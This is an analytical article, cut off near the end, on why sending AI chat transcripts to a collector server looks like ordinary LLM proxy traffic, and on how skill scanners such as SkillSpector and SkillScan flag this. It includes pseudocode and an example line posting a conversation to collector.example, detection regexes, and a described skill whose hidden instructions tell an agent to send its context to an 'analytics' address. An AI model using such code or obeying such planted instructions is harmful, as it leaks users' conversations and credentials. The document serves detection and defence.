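# Why forwarding chat transcripts to an outside server is hard to tell from ordinary LLM proxy traffic

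## What a chat request contains and what an LLM proxy does with it

A large language model (LLM) such as Claude or GPT usually runs on its provider's servers. A chat window, a coding assistant or an automated agent sends the conversation over the internet as a request and gets the model's next message back. Many of these programs send the request through an LLM proxy, a server that passes it on and returns the reply, instead of contacting the provider directly. LLM proxies are also called gateways, relays or routers.

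Using a hosted model, with or without a proxy, requires transcript forwarding, which means sending a remote server some or all of a conversation, including the output of any tools the model has used. A browser extension or an agent add-on can steal the same conversation by sending it to a server whose owner collects other people's chats. This theft can be hard to tell from normal service by inspecting the code or the network traffic, because both can send the same data in the same way.

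### Why the client sends everything again

Anthropic's main programming interface for Claude, the Messages API, is stateless, according to the developer guide *Using the Messages API*. The server keeps nothing of the conversation between requests, so the client (the program on the user's side) sends the full history every time. OpenAI's *Conversation state* likewise describes each text-generation request as independent and stateless. In an example from Anthropic's guide, a first request containing only a greeting is 12 input tokens long (tokens are the word fragments in which models read text). The next request repeats the greeting and the model's answer, adds a question, and is 30 tokens long.

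Resent text adds up quickly with agents. In Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, the model can answer the user or ask for a tool call, such as running a shell command (Bolin, 2026, *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*). For a tool call, the client runs the command, appends the output to everything it sent before, and sends it all again. One instruction from the user can set off hundreds of these rounds. If every round adds *k* tokens, then *n* rounds send *k* + 2*k* + … + *nk* = *kn*(*n* + 1)/2 tokens in total. With 2,000 new tokens a round, a conversation that ends at 100,000 tokens after 50 rounds has sent about 2.55 million. A file that the agent reads in the second round is sent again in each of the 48 later rounds.

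Some requests don't carry the full history. Codex replaces the history with a shorter version once it passes a set length. OpenAI also lets a client send the identifier of the previous response instead of the old messages, and Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026) date the beta of a similar feature, message threads, to 2 November 2026. With either feature, the transcript still leaves the user's machine, but in parts, and the provider has to store it. OpenAI saves responses for 30 days by default, while an Anthropic thread expires five minutes after its last request. Codex doesn't use the OpenAI option. Bolin writes that this is mainly to keep requests stateless and to serve customers who have opted out of data retention.

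So an agent that is working normally sends long, repetitive uploads that keep growing. They can also be very large. Anthropic raised the maximum request size from 32 MB to 128 MB on 28 October 2026.

### One request, field by field

Here is a simplified request in Anthropic's API format. A developer has asked a coding agent about a database fault, and the agent has already made one tool call.

```
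POST /v1/messages
Authorization: Bearer KEY-OF-THE-SENDER

{
  "model": "some-model",
  "max_tokens": 1024,
  "system": "You are a coding assistant. Directory: /home/ana/shop",
  "tools": [
    {"name": "shell",
     "description": "Runs a shell command and returns its output",
     "input_schema": {"type": "object",
                      "properties": {"command": {"type": "string"}}}}
  ],
  "messages": [
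    {"role": "user",
     "content": "Why can't the app reach the database?"},
    {"role": "assistant",
     "content": [{"type": "tool_use", "id": "call_1", "name": "shell",
                  "input": {"command": "cat .env"}}]},
    {"role": "user",
     "content": [{"type": "tool_result", "tool_use_id": "call_1",
                  "content": "DB_HOST=db-1\nDB_PASSWORD=example"}]}
  ]
}
```

The authorisation header comes before the message body and carries a secret key that identifies the account to bill. Anyone who receives the request also gets this key. Anthropic's own interface also accepts the key in a header called x-api-key.

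The `model` field names the model that should answer, and `max_tokens` caps the length of the answer. The `system` field holds standing instructions, which the client usually writes and doesn't show to the user. Coding agents also add facts about the machine. For example, Codex inserts the working directory and shell type before the user's first message, and in Bolin's example the directory path contains his username.

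The `tools` field lists the actions the model may ask the client to perform, each with a name, a description and a schema for its inputs. It includes any extra tools the user has connected, so it also reveals which other services the user works with.

`messages` is the transcript. The first entry is the only thing Ana typed. The second is the model's request to print a file named `.env`, where programs commonly keep passwords and keys. The model can't open the file itself, so the client ran the command on Ana's machine and put the output in the third entry. That entry has the role "user", although Ana never typed it and may never have seen it. Her database password is now part of the conversation, so the client will send it with every later request until the conversation ends or the client shortens the transcript.

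Nothing has gone wrong here, because the agent needed the file to find the fault. Users also paste secrets in by hand. *WildCode Revisited* (2025), a study of security in AI-written code, searched a collection of users' coding chats for credentials with a pattern filter and a trained classifier, then checked the results by hand. Of 209 conversations, 111 held real secrets, and in 84 of those the user had supplied them. Because the search had picked out suspicious chats, these figures don't give a rate for chats in general, but they do show that real keys appear in ordinary use.

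Coding agents can be designed to send less to a remote model. *Teaching Code Agents to Ask Without Leaking Private Code* (2026) builds on a design in which a small model on the developer's machine does all the editing and testing, and asks a larger remote model only for advice. Those questions can still contain private names, file paths and source code. The paper presents a way to train the small model to include fewer of them, but most users have no such filter.

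### From the client to the provider and back

A model client sends its requests to a network address called the endpoint, which is specified by a setting called the base URL. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, reads the base URL from a variable named `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, while Codex reads its endpoint from a configuration file. Xie, Wu and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Proxy Knows Too Much* that an unmodified client can switch providers by changing only the endpoint. The same change can send the client's requests through a proxy.

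Suppose Ana's employer runs one. Her request then takes this route:

1. The client opens an encrypted connection to the proxy and sends the request with a credential that the proxy issued to her.
2. The proxy checks the credential, picks one of the employer's accounts with a model provider, and attaches that account's key.
3. The proxy opens a second encrypted connection, to the provider, and sends the request on.
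4. The provider streams the reply back. The proxy relays it and records how many tokens Ana used.
5. The client reads the reply as if it had come straight from the provider, runs whatever tool the model asked for, and sends the next, longer request.

The encryption in the first and third steps is TLS, the protocol behind the padlock in a web browser. TLS protects data between the two ends of one connection, and here there are two connections:

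```
client ===== TLS 1 =====> LLM proxy ===== TLS 2 =====> provider
                         (plain text)
```

Somebody tapping the network on either side of the proxy sees only scrambled data. Inside the proxy the whole exchange lies open, including the prompt, the file contents, the database password and the reply. That isn't a flaw in the set-up. The first connection ends at the proxy because the client addressed it there, and the proxy needs the request in readable form to swap the keys and choose a provider. (A corporate network proxy is a different thing. It can pass an encrypted connection along without opening it.)

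The proxy may also hold the user's own credential. According to Anthropic's Claude Code documentation, if a developer changes the base URL without setting a credential for the proxy, a saved personal login stays active, and the proxy must forward it to Anthropic for the requests to work.

Ana can't check much of this from her end. Claude Code treats the proxy as if it were the Claude interface and, according to Anthropic's guidance for proxy operators, can't tell which provider is behind it. Xie and colleagues note that an agent also can't tell whether it got the provider's exact reply or a substitute. *Your Agent Is Mine* (Liu, Shou and colleagues, 2026) adds that no provider enforces a cryptographic check between client and model that would expose tampering. It also reports that some commercial and free routers were caught abusing their position between the two.

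Xie and colleagues built a proxy whose operator can't read the conversations passing through it. The client's connection ends inside an enclave, a region of the processor that even the machine's owner can't look into. Before sending any of the conversation, the client checks a cryptographic fingerprint of the enclave's code, which an ordinary proxy doesn't let it do. The check only shows which code is running, so somebody still has to read that code and decide that it is harmless. The operator can still see token counts, sizes and timing, and the design adds about six milliseconds per request.

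### Why people use proxies

Careful organisations install proxies on purpose, even though a proxy can see so much. Anthropic lists five reasons for a company to do so. The provider's key stays on the server, so developers never hold it, and the company can end a departing employee's access by cancelling one credential. The company can also see who uses how much, set budgets and rate limits, log every model request for compliance, and switch provider without reconfiguring anyone's laptop.

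People who run a model on their own hardware use the same base URL setting. Popular programs for serving local models accept requests in OpenAI's format, so the client works as before when the user points it at their own machine. The server may then be a process on the same laptop as the client.

Some companies go further and forbid requests to any other address. An administrator can fix the base URL in Claude Code's managed settings, and a developer cannot override it from the command line. According to Anthropic, one more setting makes Claude Code refuse any session that points elsewhere, including to Anthropic itself. On such a machine, a request that follows company rules may go to an address that no outsider has heard of.

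An unfamiliar server address is weak evidence of theft. Anthropic doesn't endorse or audit other companies' proxies, so it offers no approved list to check the address against. Stored transcripts are also weak evidence, because a company that logs requests for compliance keeps them deliberately.

### The same transfer, written twice

The pseudocode on the left sends a conversation to a model through a proxy, while the pseudocode on the right sends the same conversation to a collector, a server that only stores what it receives.

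```
CALLING A PROXY                     SENDING TO A COLLECTOR

url   = settings.base_url           url   = COLLECTOR_URL
body  = {"model": model,            body  = {"model": model,
         "messages": history}                "messages": history}
reply = post(url, key, body)        post(url, key, body)
history.append(reply)
```

| | Proxy | Collector | |
|---|---|---|---|
| Data sent | Full message history | Full message history | Identical |
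| Method | Encrypted web request with a key | Encrypted web request with a key | Identical |
| Who chose the address | The user or employer, in a setting | The program's author | Differs |
| Use of the reply | Becomes the next message | None | Differs |
| What the recipient keeps | Usage records, perhaps full logs | The transcript | Differs, but not in the code |

The unused reply seems to be the best clue, and a careless thief will leave it, but it is easy to remove. If the collector passes the conversation to a real model and returns the answer, the program on the right can use the reply just as the one on the left does, and the user gets a working assistant. An unused reply also doesn't prove theft, because crash reporters and logging services ignore replies for good reasons.

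The address is a weaker clue than it looks. A legitimate vendor may write its own proxy's address into its product, and a malicious installer can put an attacker's address in the settings file, so that the unmodified code on the left sends transcripts to the attacker. Knowing what the recipient keeps would often settle the question, but those records are on someone else's computer. None of the three clues is decisive on its own.

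### Exfiltration depends on authorisation

OpenSSF's *Exfiltration* (2025), a glossary entry from the Open Source Security Foundation, uses the definition given by NIST, the US standards institute, which is the "unauthorized transfer of information from a system". NIST calls the innocent counterpart *information exchange*, meaning access to data, or its transfer, beyond a system's authorisation boundaries "in order to accomplish a mission or business function". Data crosses a boundary in both cases, but the first definition depends on a missing permission and the second on a purpose, neither of which is a property of the bytes.

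*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026), a study of malicious tools for agents, defines remote data exfiltration as sending the user's prompt and the record of the agent's actions to "attacker-controlled remote endpoints". Without the words "attacker-controlled", the definition would fit any client of a hosted model.

Exfiltration is the transfer of data to a party that the data's owner has not authorised to receive it. The owner may not be the user. A developer who routes company code through a cheap proxy found on a forum has consented to the transfer, but the employer, who owns the code, has not. Exfiltration can also follow an authorised transfer. If an approved proxy sells its logs to a buyer the owner has not authorised, inspecting the user's machine will not reveal the sale.

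### Agent skills and rule-based scanners

Much of the code that raises this question reaches users as agent skills. A skill is a package of written instructions, often with scripts, that an AI agent loads and follows with the user's privileges. Agent Skills' *Specification* defines it as a folder containing a `SKILL.md` file and, optionally, programs and reference documents. The agent reads each skill's name and description at startup, the full instructions when a task calls for the skill, and the other files only as needed. Once a script runs, it has the agent's access to the disk, including stored passwords. The conversation is harder to access because, according to Hu and colleagues, a tool typically doesn't see the user's prompt or the agent's earlier steps unless the agent passes them in. However, a skill can include plain-English instructions for the agent to pass the conversation to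 a script, whether for a legitimate purpose or a malicious one.

Because anyone can publish a skill, users and marketplaces check skills with rule-based scanners, which flag code or text that matches fixed patterns without judging its purpose. The skill marketplace ClawHub, for example, shows findings from NVIDIA's *SkillSpector* on skills' audit pages. SkillSpector's first stage looks for 64 patterns. One of them, External Transmission, covers sending data to outside addresses and has medium severity. Another, Context Leakage, has high severity and is described as "Transmitting conversation context externally", which a program that talks to an LLM proxy does on every turn. Under the published weights, a skill with a script and one finding of each kind scores 45.5 out of 100, and SkillSpector recommends caution. Another high-severity finding, for file contents that flow to the network, raises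 the score to 78, and SkillSpector recommends not installing the skill, although a legitimate client for a coding agent could match all three patterns.

NVIDIA describes this first stage as having high recall (the share of bad items that it flags) and moderate precision (the share of flagged items that are bad). An optional second stage uses a language model to assess context and intent. This raises precision to about 87% across all patterns combined, so roughly one flag in eight is still a false positive. To run the second stage, SkillSpector has to send material from the skill to a model, whose address the user can set with the `OPENAI_BASE_URL` variable.

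## Relay To Agent: an openly described relay that a scanner flags

Relay To Agent is a small ClawHub skill that lets an AI agent send messages to another model and read the answers. Santos's public listing for the skill, *Relay To Agent*, describes it as a client for any service that accepts requests in OpenAI's format. The compatible services he lists include two hosted services, Connect Chat and OpenRouter, and three programs that people can run on their own machines. The listing showed only 13 current installs in March 2026, but the skill is a convenient test case because ClawHub has published several scanners' results for it.

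A call to the skill works like this:

1. The user's agent runs a script, `relay.mjs`, with a message and the name of the agent or model that should answer.
2. The script takes the base URL from a variable called `RELAY_BASE_URL` or, if that is empty, from a file called `agents.json`. It takes the key from `RELAY_API_KEY`.
3. It loads up to 50 earlier messages from a session file in the user's home directory.
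4. It sends those messages and the new one to the base URL, along with the key.
5. It returns the reply and saves the longer conversation to the session file.

The script forwards what the user's agent passes to it, plus the history of that exchange. It doesn't collect everything the user has said to the agent in their separate conversation.

### Five findings

ClawHub's *Relay To Agent* audit page lists five SkillSpector findings:

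| Finding | Category | Severity | Confidence | What SkillSpector flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Missing User Warnings | None shown | Medium | 95% | The description has no warning that prompts and history may leave the machine and stay on disk |
| Missing User Warnings | None shown | Medium | 93% | The script saves full transcripts without notice, consent or tighter file permissions |
| Missing User Warnings | None shown | Medium | 95% | The script sends the message and earlier history without a warning at that moment |
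| External Transmission | Data Exfiltration | Medium | 88% | A configuration line with the base URL `api.example.com/v1` |
| External Transmission | Data Exfiltration | Medium | 89% | A configuration line with the base URL `api.connectchat.ai/api` |

Both External Transmission findings are for lines that send nothing. The first flags a placeholder address from the instructions, on a domain reserved for documentation. The second flags a Connect Chat address that seems to come from the configuration file supplied with the skill. The scanner did not flag the `createChatCompletion` call, which sends the conversation, for External Transmission.

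A tutorial by the cloud company GreenNode offers a likely explanation. In version 2.8.1 of SkillSpector, the External Transmission rule consists of nine regular expressions, which are patterns for matching text. One of them matches any web address whose host name starts with `api.`, as both flagged addresses do. ClawHub may have run a different version, and in 2.8.1 this expression starts at 50% confidence, so some other step or setting must account for the 88% and 89%. The confidence figure can't be the probability that the skill steals data, because a placeholder address scored 88%.

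The Missing User Warnings findings probably come from SkillSpector's model-based second stage. They match none of the 64 patterns NVIDIA published, and each comes with a paragraph of reasoning about this skill. GreenNode describes a group of "quality policy" checks that run only when a model is available, and these findings would fit there.

The same five findings can lead to different recommendations depending on how SkillSpector adds them up. NVIDIA's published formula gives five medium findings in a skill with a script a score of 5 × 10 × 1.3 = 65 out of 100, which means "do not install". GreenNode found that the code of version 2.8.1 produces lower scores. It multiplies each finding's points by its confidence, halves the points for the second finding from the same rule and quarters those for the third, and applies the factor of 1.3 only to findings in executable files. If the three warnings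 count as one rule, the total falls to between 29 and 38, and the recommendation becomes "caution".

### Disclosure complaints and a real bug

Santos begins his instructions by explaining that the skill sends messages to agents on an outside endpoint, and he gives the folder where it stores sessions and the 50-message limit. SkillSpector's second finding, that the script keeps transcripts "without any disclosure", is therefore wrong about the disclosure. It also conflicts with the first finding, which describes the local cache as documented.

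Some of the criticism is valid. Santos writes that the other agent "remembers context", and a user could easily miss that this means sending the old messages again every time. A warning at the moment of sending might not help much, though, because the user's agent runs the script and would see the warning first. These complaints concern how well the user understands what they are agreeing to, and they don't show that the conversation reaches anyone the user hasn't chosen.

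ClawHub's own review system, ClawScan, found an actual bug that isn't among SkillSpector's five findings. ClawScan uses a language model to assess a skill's files and the other scanners' results, without running the skill. Its review of 10 May, in ClawHub's *Relay To Agent* (2026), quotes the code that inserts the session name into a file path without checking it. In a path, `..` means "go up one folder". Given the session name `x/../../../../notes`, the script would open `notes.json` in the user's home directory instead of a file in its cache.

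The script would then treat that file's contents as earlier messages, and could send them to the endpoint and then overwrite the file. ClawScan recommends rejecting session names that contain slashes or `..`, and checking that the final path is still inside the cache folder. This would prevent unrelated files from leaking this way, but the skill would still send conversations to the same address.

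The bug also seems to explain why the skill's rating got worse. In March, a ClawHub scan rated version 0.0.1 benign with high confidence and found that everything the skill requested matched its purpose. In May the status was "Review", although the version number was the same and the script had been forwarding transcripts all along.

### What ClawHub tells the user

ClawHub's overview says the skill "mostly does what it says" and names the file-path bug as the exception. It advises people to install the skill only if they are "comfortable sending prompts and retained session history to the configured AI endpoint". It also tells them to keep secrets and regulated data out of messages and to use base URLs they trust.

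This leaves the main decision to the user, and ClawHub could hardly avoid that, because the user can set the base URL after installation, when the audit is over. The destination might be a program on the same laptop or a stranger's server. The key goes there too, so someone who enters an OpenAI key but leaves Connect Chat's address in the configuration file would send that key to Connect Chat.

ClawHub's audit of another chat skill, *Pywayne Llm Chat Bot*, is similar. That skill also sends prompts to a configurable endpoint, which ClawScan describes as "disclosed and central to the skill purpose", and the user again has to decide whether to trust the endpoint.

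The antivirus result is weak evidence that Relay To Agent is safe. All 66 vendors on VirusTotal, a service that runs files through many antivirus engines, marked the skill clean. In a written assessment included in ClawHub's *Relay To Agent* (2026), VirusTotal calls it a "straightforward relay" and finds no evidence of data exfiltration. But antivirus engines mostly look for known malware and addresses with a bad reputation. A newly written program that collected transcripts and sent them to a new address through ordinary web requests could also pass.

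OpenClaw, the project behind ClawHub, shows SkillSpector findings as advisories that don't automatically block a skill. It mentions one skill with 173 findings that ClawScan labelled suspicious but not malicious. According to OpenClaw's *Security Audits*, the main question is coherence, meaning whether a skill's name, description, requested access and contents match what users would expect. A "Review" result means users should read the findings before installing, though the skill may still be legitimate. A separate risk level describes how much power the skill has, regardless of its author's intent.

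*ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) compared the scanners' results on 67,453 skills. Of the skills that ClawScan rated clean, 32.7% had a SkillSpector advisory. One of them, which copies a user's meeting notes to local files, had the maximum risk score of 100.

The paper also reports that clean skills had slightly more Data Exfiltration findings (1,196) than suspicious ones (996), because much of the data flow was disclosed and served the skill's purpose. These counts are a little misleading, since there were far more clean skills. The finding appeared in 2.9% of clean skills and 3.9% of suspicious ones, so it still separates the groups poorly. Dangerous Code Execution, by comparison, appeared in 0.7% of clean skills and 5.2% of suspicious ones.

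Neither comparison measures accuracy, because a language model assigned the verdicts and people did not check them all. The advisories can also miss the worst cases. SkillSpector had flagged only 14 of the 206 skills with a malicious verdict, while VirusTotal had flagged most of them.

### Changing one fact at a time

Small changes to Relay To Agent would show what the findings depend on. The table gives predictions based on the published rules and GreenNode's reading of the code, not the results of scans.

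| Change | External Transmission | Missing User Warnings | New finding to expect | Unauthorised recipient? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Santos replaces both example addresses with a local one | Both probably disappear | Stay | None | No |
| Santos adds prominent warnings | Both stay | Should mostly disappear | None | No |
| A malicious installer changes `RELAY_BASE_URL` on the user's machine | Both stay | Stay | None | Yes |
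| The script ignores the setting and uses a fixed, hidden address | Both stay, perhaps with a third | Stay, with different wording | Description-Behavior Mismatch | Yes |
| The script secretly sends a copy to a second server | Both stay, perhaps with a third | Stay, with different wording | Description-Behavior Mismatch | Yes |

The file-path bug would be there in every row.

Santos could resolve most of the report's findings by editing text, and every conversation would still go to the same place. The malicious installer could redirect every conversation to an address that is never in the files ClawHub scans, so the report would stay the same.

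If the code used a fixed hidden address, it would contradict the description, which promises a configurable endpoint. SkillSpector's rule for this, Description-Behavior Mismatch, is the only one of its 64 rules that NVIDIA marks as powered by a language model. Its severity is medium, the same as for the placeholder address. Whether SkillSpector also reported External Transmission would depend on how the author wrote the address and the sending code. A host name that didn't begin with `api.` would avoid the expression that seems to have matched here, though one of the other eight expressions might still match.

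ClawScan's verdict would be more likely to change, because ClawScan checks whether a skill's behaviour matches its description. Koc and colleagues describe a genuine remote control for Roku televisions, published by a known OpenClaw maintainer, that ClawScan rated suspicious. The skill included poorly disclosed ways to send it commands through Telegram. ClawScan should rate a skill with a hidden recipient for users' conversations at least as suspicious, if it detects the recipient.

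A secret second recipient would be harder for the user to notice, since the chosen model would still answer normally. It would also contradict the skill's description, so the same mismatch rule should apply. But the code that copies the messages might not be in the skill's own files. Relay To Agent sends its requests through a separate library, `openai-fetch`, which the user may have to download during setup. SkillSpector scans the skill's files and checks its dependencies against a database of known vulnerabilities. If someone added the copying code to the library, SkillSpector's findings could all stay the same until somebody reported the problem.

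The mismatch rule also needs the model stage to run. GreenNode scanned a harmless sample skill without supplying credentials for a model. Three model-based checks failed, but the headline result was still 0 out of 100 and "safe". The report listed the failures further down.

### Who reviews conversation leakage

NVIDIA based SkillSpector on the research behind an earlier scanner, SkillScan. Two of SkillSpector's high-severity rules, Context Leakage and Exfiltration Commands, cover conversations leaving the machine. Exfiltration Commands covers written instructions to send them out. Relay To Agent sends conversation history to an outside address, but neither finding appears in the audit. The patterns may have missed the code, or the model stage may have removed a match as a false positive.

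NVIDIA's *Scan Agent Skills Before Installation* describes how the scanner splits the work between fixed checks and a language model. The fixed checks look for suspicious strings, risky dependencies, dangerous functions and permissions that don't match the code. The language model compares a skill's stated purpose with what its code appears to do, and looks for vague triggers and subtle policy problems.

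The guide tells publishers to block a release with any critical or high-severity finding "until fixed or formally accepted". This general rule covers Context Leakage, and formal acceptance presumably needs a person to sign off, but the guide doesn't send all conversation leakage to manual review. The rule doesn't cover a medium-severity External Transmission finding. When a description doesn't match the code, the guide recommends changing one or the other. Koc and colleagues write that disputed skills frequently need human judgement about disclosure and intent, but they mean disputed skills in general.

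By July 2026, NVIDIA had added a way to accept known findings so that later scans report only new ones. This would help the developer of an honest relay, who could otherwise see the same External Transmission findings after every update. The developer can accept individual findings or a whole rule, but accepting the whole rule would also hide an External Transmission finding for a second recipient added later.

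## SkillScan: what pattern rules and human reviewers made of 31,132 skills

In *Agent Skills in the Wild*, Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026) surveyed two public skill marketplaces in December 2025 using SkillScan, the scanner behind several of SkillSpector's rules. They collected 42,447 skills and kept 31,132 after removing duplicates, very short skills, those not in English, and 7,353 whose code was no longer online. Platforms may have taken down some of the missing skills for being malicious, so the survey could understate the problem.

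SkillScan found at least one vulnerability in 8,126 skills, or 26.1%. "Vulnerability" here covers deliberate theft, careless code, and code that could do harm whatever its author intended, because SkillScan can't reliably tell these apart. Nearly half of the 8,126 had only low-severity problems, such as a dependency without a fixed version number.

### Three stages and two thresholds

SkillScan works in three stages:

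1. A rule-based scanner searches each skill's instructions and scripts with regular expressions and keyword lists.
2. LLM-Guard, an open-source library, runs ten text filters. They look for things like secrets, invisible characters, disguised code and prompt injection (text written to take control of a model).
3. If either stage finds something, the skill becomes a candidate. A language model, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, then receives the whole skill and returns a verdict, a confidence between 0 and 1, and its evidence.

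The first two stages passed 12,847 candidates to the model, about 41% of all the skills. The rule-based scanner, which uses regular expressions, flagged 11,575 of them on its own, LLM-Guard flagged 1,144 on its own, and both flagged the other 128. The remaining 18,285 skills never reached the model.

The model needs less confidence to confirm a finding than to dismiss one. A confidence of 0.6 is enough to confirm, but dismissing a finding from the rules takes 0.8. Suppose a rule matches the line where an honest relay sends its messages. If the model calls the relay harmless with a confidence of 0.75, the finding stands, while at 0.85 it goes away. (The paper also defines a flagged skill as one with a *vulnerable* verdict of at least 0.6, which is hard to square with this rule.)

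Liu and colleagues chose the higher threshold because they preferred false alarms to missed attacks, and because a reassuring explanation in a skill might fool the model. They report that this choice cut the model's wrongful dismissals by 23% in their validation set. They also argue that rules are rarely wrong about unambiguous signs, such as a command that downloads a script and runs it immediately. The same 0.8 threshold also applies to ordinary web requests, which are much more ambiguous.

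The total excludes another 1,203 candidates as uncertain because they had confidence scores between 0.4 and 0.6. In a manual check of 50 of these, 22 were vulnerable, 19 were harmless, and the human experts disagreed on the other nine.

Claude 3.5 Sonnet's verdicts also varied. In a test on 200 skills, 11 verdicts changed when the researchers reran the same prompt, and 18 changed when they reworded it. In all, 22 skills had a verdict that changed in at least one of these tests. The model is far behind current ones, so a newer one might do better, but the researchers advised relying on the fixed rules where results have to be reproducible.

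### One pattern, two transfers

The paper gives this simplified pattern for sending data over the web:

```
requests\.(post|put).*http[s]?://
```

It looks for a call to `requests`, a popular Python library, that uses one of two common methods for sending data and has a web address later on the same line. Here it is applied to a call to an LLM proxy and to a theft:

```
PROXY   reply = requests.post("https://proxy.example/v1/chat", json=body)
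THEFT   requests.post("https://collector.example/v1/chat", json=body)

Part of pattern    Text in PROXY       Text in THEFT
requests\.         requests.           requests.
(post|put)         post                post
.*                 ("                  ("
http[s]?://        https://            https://
```

Both lines match. The match begins after `reply =` and ends just before the server's name, so it leaves out the only two differences between the lines.

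The pattern can also miss both transfers. Most proxy clients read the address from a setting, so the call looks more like `requests.post(base_url + "/chat", json=body)`, which the pattern doesn't match because it contains no `https://`. A thief can write the call the same way. In five of the 11 vulnerable skills that SkillScan missed in validation, the code built its web address from separate pieces of text.

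The simplified pattern would miss even the paper's own example of External Transmission, a monitoring script from a real skill that posts alerts and the computer's name to an address in a configuration file. One of the full scanner's unpublished rules may have flagged the script, or the model may have supplied the label. The label is still odd, because the paper defines External Transmission as sending data to a *hardcoded* address, and whoever configures this script chooses the address.

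*Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up by an overlapping team, includes a version of the pattern that skips addresses starting with `localhost`, the usual name for the user's own machine. This exempts some programs that talk to a local model, but not those that use a company's proxy or call a local model by its numeric address, 127.0.0.1.

A proxy client usually also needs a key, which it often reads from an environment variable. SkillScan's simplified pattern for these variables, `os\.environ\[.*\]`, matches any such read, so a legitimate client could also receive a high-severity finding for harvesting secrets. *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026), which describes a library of skills for researchers, treats this as a systematic false positive because the skill reads its own key and calls its own service. Of the 11 skills in the library with a critical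 finding, eight declared such a variable in their headers.

The follow-up study treats the same combination as a sign of intent. Of its 157 confirmed malicious skills, 58 both harvested credentials and sent data out, and a skill that did one was more likely to do the other (odds ratio 2.24). But because that comparison included only malicious skills, it can't show whether the combination distinguishes them from benign ones. The experience with the research library suggests that it often doesn't.

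### Is sending a conversation always high severity?

SkillScan sorts vulnerabilities into 14 patterns in four categories: prompt injection, data exfiltration, privilege escalation and supply-chain risk. Three of the patterns can apply to transcript forwarding:

| Code | Pattern | What it covers | Severity | Skills |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| E1 | External Transmission | A script sends collected data to a fixed outside address | Medium | 89 |
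| E4 | Context Leakage | A script sends the agent's conversation to an outside service | High | 28 |
| P3 | Exfiltration Commands | Written instructions tell the agent to send its context out | High | 18 |

The counts don't show how common each pattern is in the marketplaces, because they come from a sample of 1,218 skills chosen to include extra skills with scripts and cases of rare problems.

A script that posts a chat history to a fixed address fits both E1, which depends on where the data goes, and E4, which depends on what the data is. Two researchers set the severity of each pattern before they looked at any skills. They rated E1 as medium because it could reflect either carelessness or an attack. A high rating means that a pattern strongly suggests malice or creates an immediate risk. A skill takes the severity of its worst pattern, and nothing in the skill's description can change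 that rating.

E4's high severity rating makes partial sense for an openly described relay like Relay To Agent. Sending a conversation to the wrong recipient can do serious damage, and because the rating is fixed, an attacker can't lower it with a friendly description. But the rating is poor evidence of malice, because the user installed the relay to send the conversation. It is better to read E4's severity as a measure of what the user could lose, and to judge intent separately, as OpenClaw does.

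Liu and colleagues describe the 1,619 skills with high-severity patterns, 5.2% of the total, as likely malicious, and NVIDIA repeats that figure on SkillSpector's project page. When the researchers manually reviewed the 87 highest-risk skills, they found clear signs of malicious intent in only 23. The other 64 did dangerous things that could have been attacks or mistakes, such as a misconfigured address in a real backup tool. The follow-up study confirmed malice in 157 of 98,380 skills, or 0.16%. That is far below 5.2%, though it is a lower bound because the study counted only skills that behaved harmfully during a short test.

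The follow-up also changed some ratings and definitions. E1 is now high severity, P3 includes context leakage, and E4 means network reconnaissance, so the same code can mean different things in two reports. The description of E1 now specifies "attacker-controlled servers", although its regular expression can't detect who controls a server. NVIDIA kept E1 at medium in its list of rules, but the sample report on the same page rates an E1 finding as high.

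The paper refers readers to Appendix H for a real case of Context Leakage (E4), but the appendix goes from E1 to E3 and has no E4 example. The paper publishes no pattern for conversations either, so the model probably assigned most of the E4 labels. The model's prompt defines E4 as broadly as SkillSpector does, without mentioning whether the user has agreed or has chosen the recipient.

The closest real example in the paper is a code-review assistant with 312 stars on GitHub. Comments hidden in its instructions told the agent to periodically send its conversation context to an "analytics" address. The paper classifies this as P2 (hidden instructions) and P3. The case is clear because the skill's author hid the instruction from the user, whereas the "analytics" address alone would have been weak evidence.

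### Accuracy on 200 skills

To measure SkillScan's accuracy, two security researchers labelled 200 skills that the team had not used to develop or tune the rules. They judged 63 to be vulnerable. The results were:

| | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Rule-based scanner alone | 71.4% | 91.2% |
| Full pipeline | 86.7% | 82.5% |

The full pipeline flagged 60 skills, of which 52 were vulnerable, and missed 11 other vulnerable ones. The paper doesn't give counts for the rules alone, but its percentages imply roughly 57 correct flags and 23 false positives. These counts are approximate because 91.2% of the 63 vulnerable skills is not a whole number. The later stages removed about 15 false positives but also dropped about five vulnerable skills.

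These figures are less certain than the paper suggests. Its margin of ±4.7 percentage points for precision matches a calculation using all 200 skills, but precision depends only on the 60 flagged ones. With those 60, the paper's own statistical method gives a range of about 76% to 93%. The range for recall, based on the 63 vulnerable skills, is about 71% to 90%.

Four of the eight false positives were legitimate security tools, and two were documentation examples that never ran. The other two were harmless telemetry or update requests that sent non-sensitive information to well-known services. The paper gives GitHub's API and PyPI, the Python package index, as examples of such services. An employer's private proxy is harder to classify because it receives whole conversations at an unfamiliar address.

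These figures cover all 14 patterns, from unpinned dependencies to hidden instructions, so they don't measure accuracy on transcript forwarding. For data exfiltration alone, precision was 91.3% and recall 86.7%, but that category also includes searching for files and collecting passwords. If Context Leakage was as common among the 200 skills as in the larger sample, there were only about five cases, far too few for a useful estimate.

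Adding a model to a scanner doesn't always improve precision. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) tested Cisco's skill scanner on 80 malicious and 60 harmless skills. The scanner flagged 33 of the harmless skills without a model and 40 with one. It also caught fewer of the malicious skills with the model.

*SkillSentry* (2026) reports that scanners using models or agents wrongly flagged between 43% and 54% of harmless skills on one benchmark. Its method checks whether an effect disappears when the skill is switched off, and whether the advertised task needs that effect. An honest relay should pass, since relaying requires sending messages, and a relay whose owner secretly keeps the messages might pass for the same reason.

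### Human agreement and its cost

The accuracy figures depend on the two researchers' labels. Both had experience in penetration testing (authorised attempts to break into systems). They worked independently, without seeing SkillScan's results, and spent 15 to 30 minutes on each skill. They disagreed on 34 of the 200 skills, or 17%, and settled those cases with a third researcher. Most disputes were over code that could be either a legitimate function or a route for an attack.

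Liu and colleagues report a Cohen's kappa of 0.83 for whether a skill was vulnerable. Kappa measures agreement beyond what chance would produce:

κ = (*p*ₒ − *p*ₑ) / (1 − *p*ₑ)

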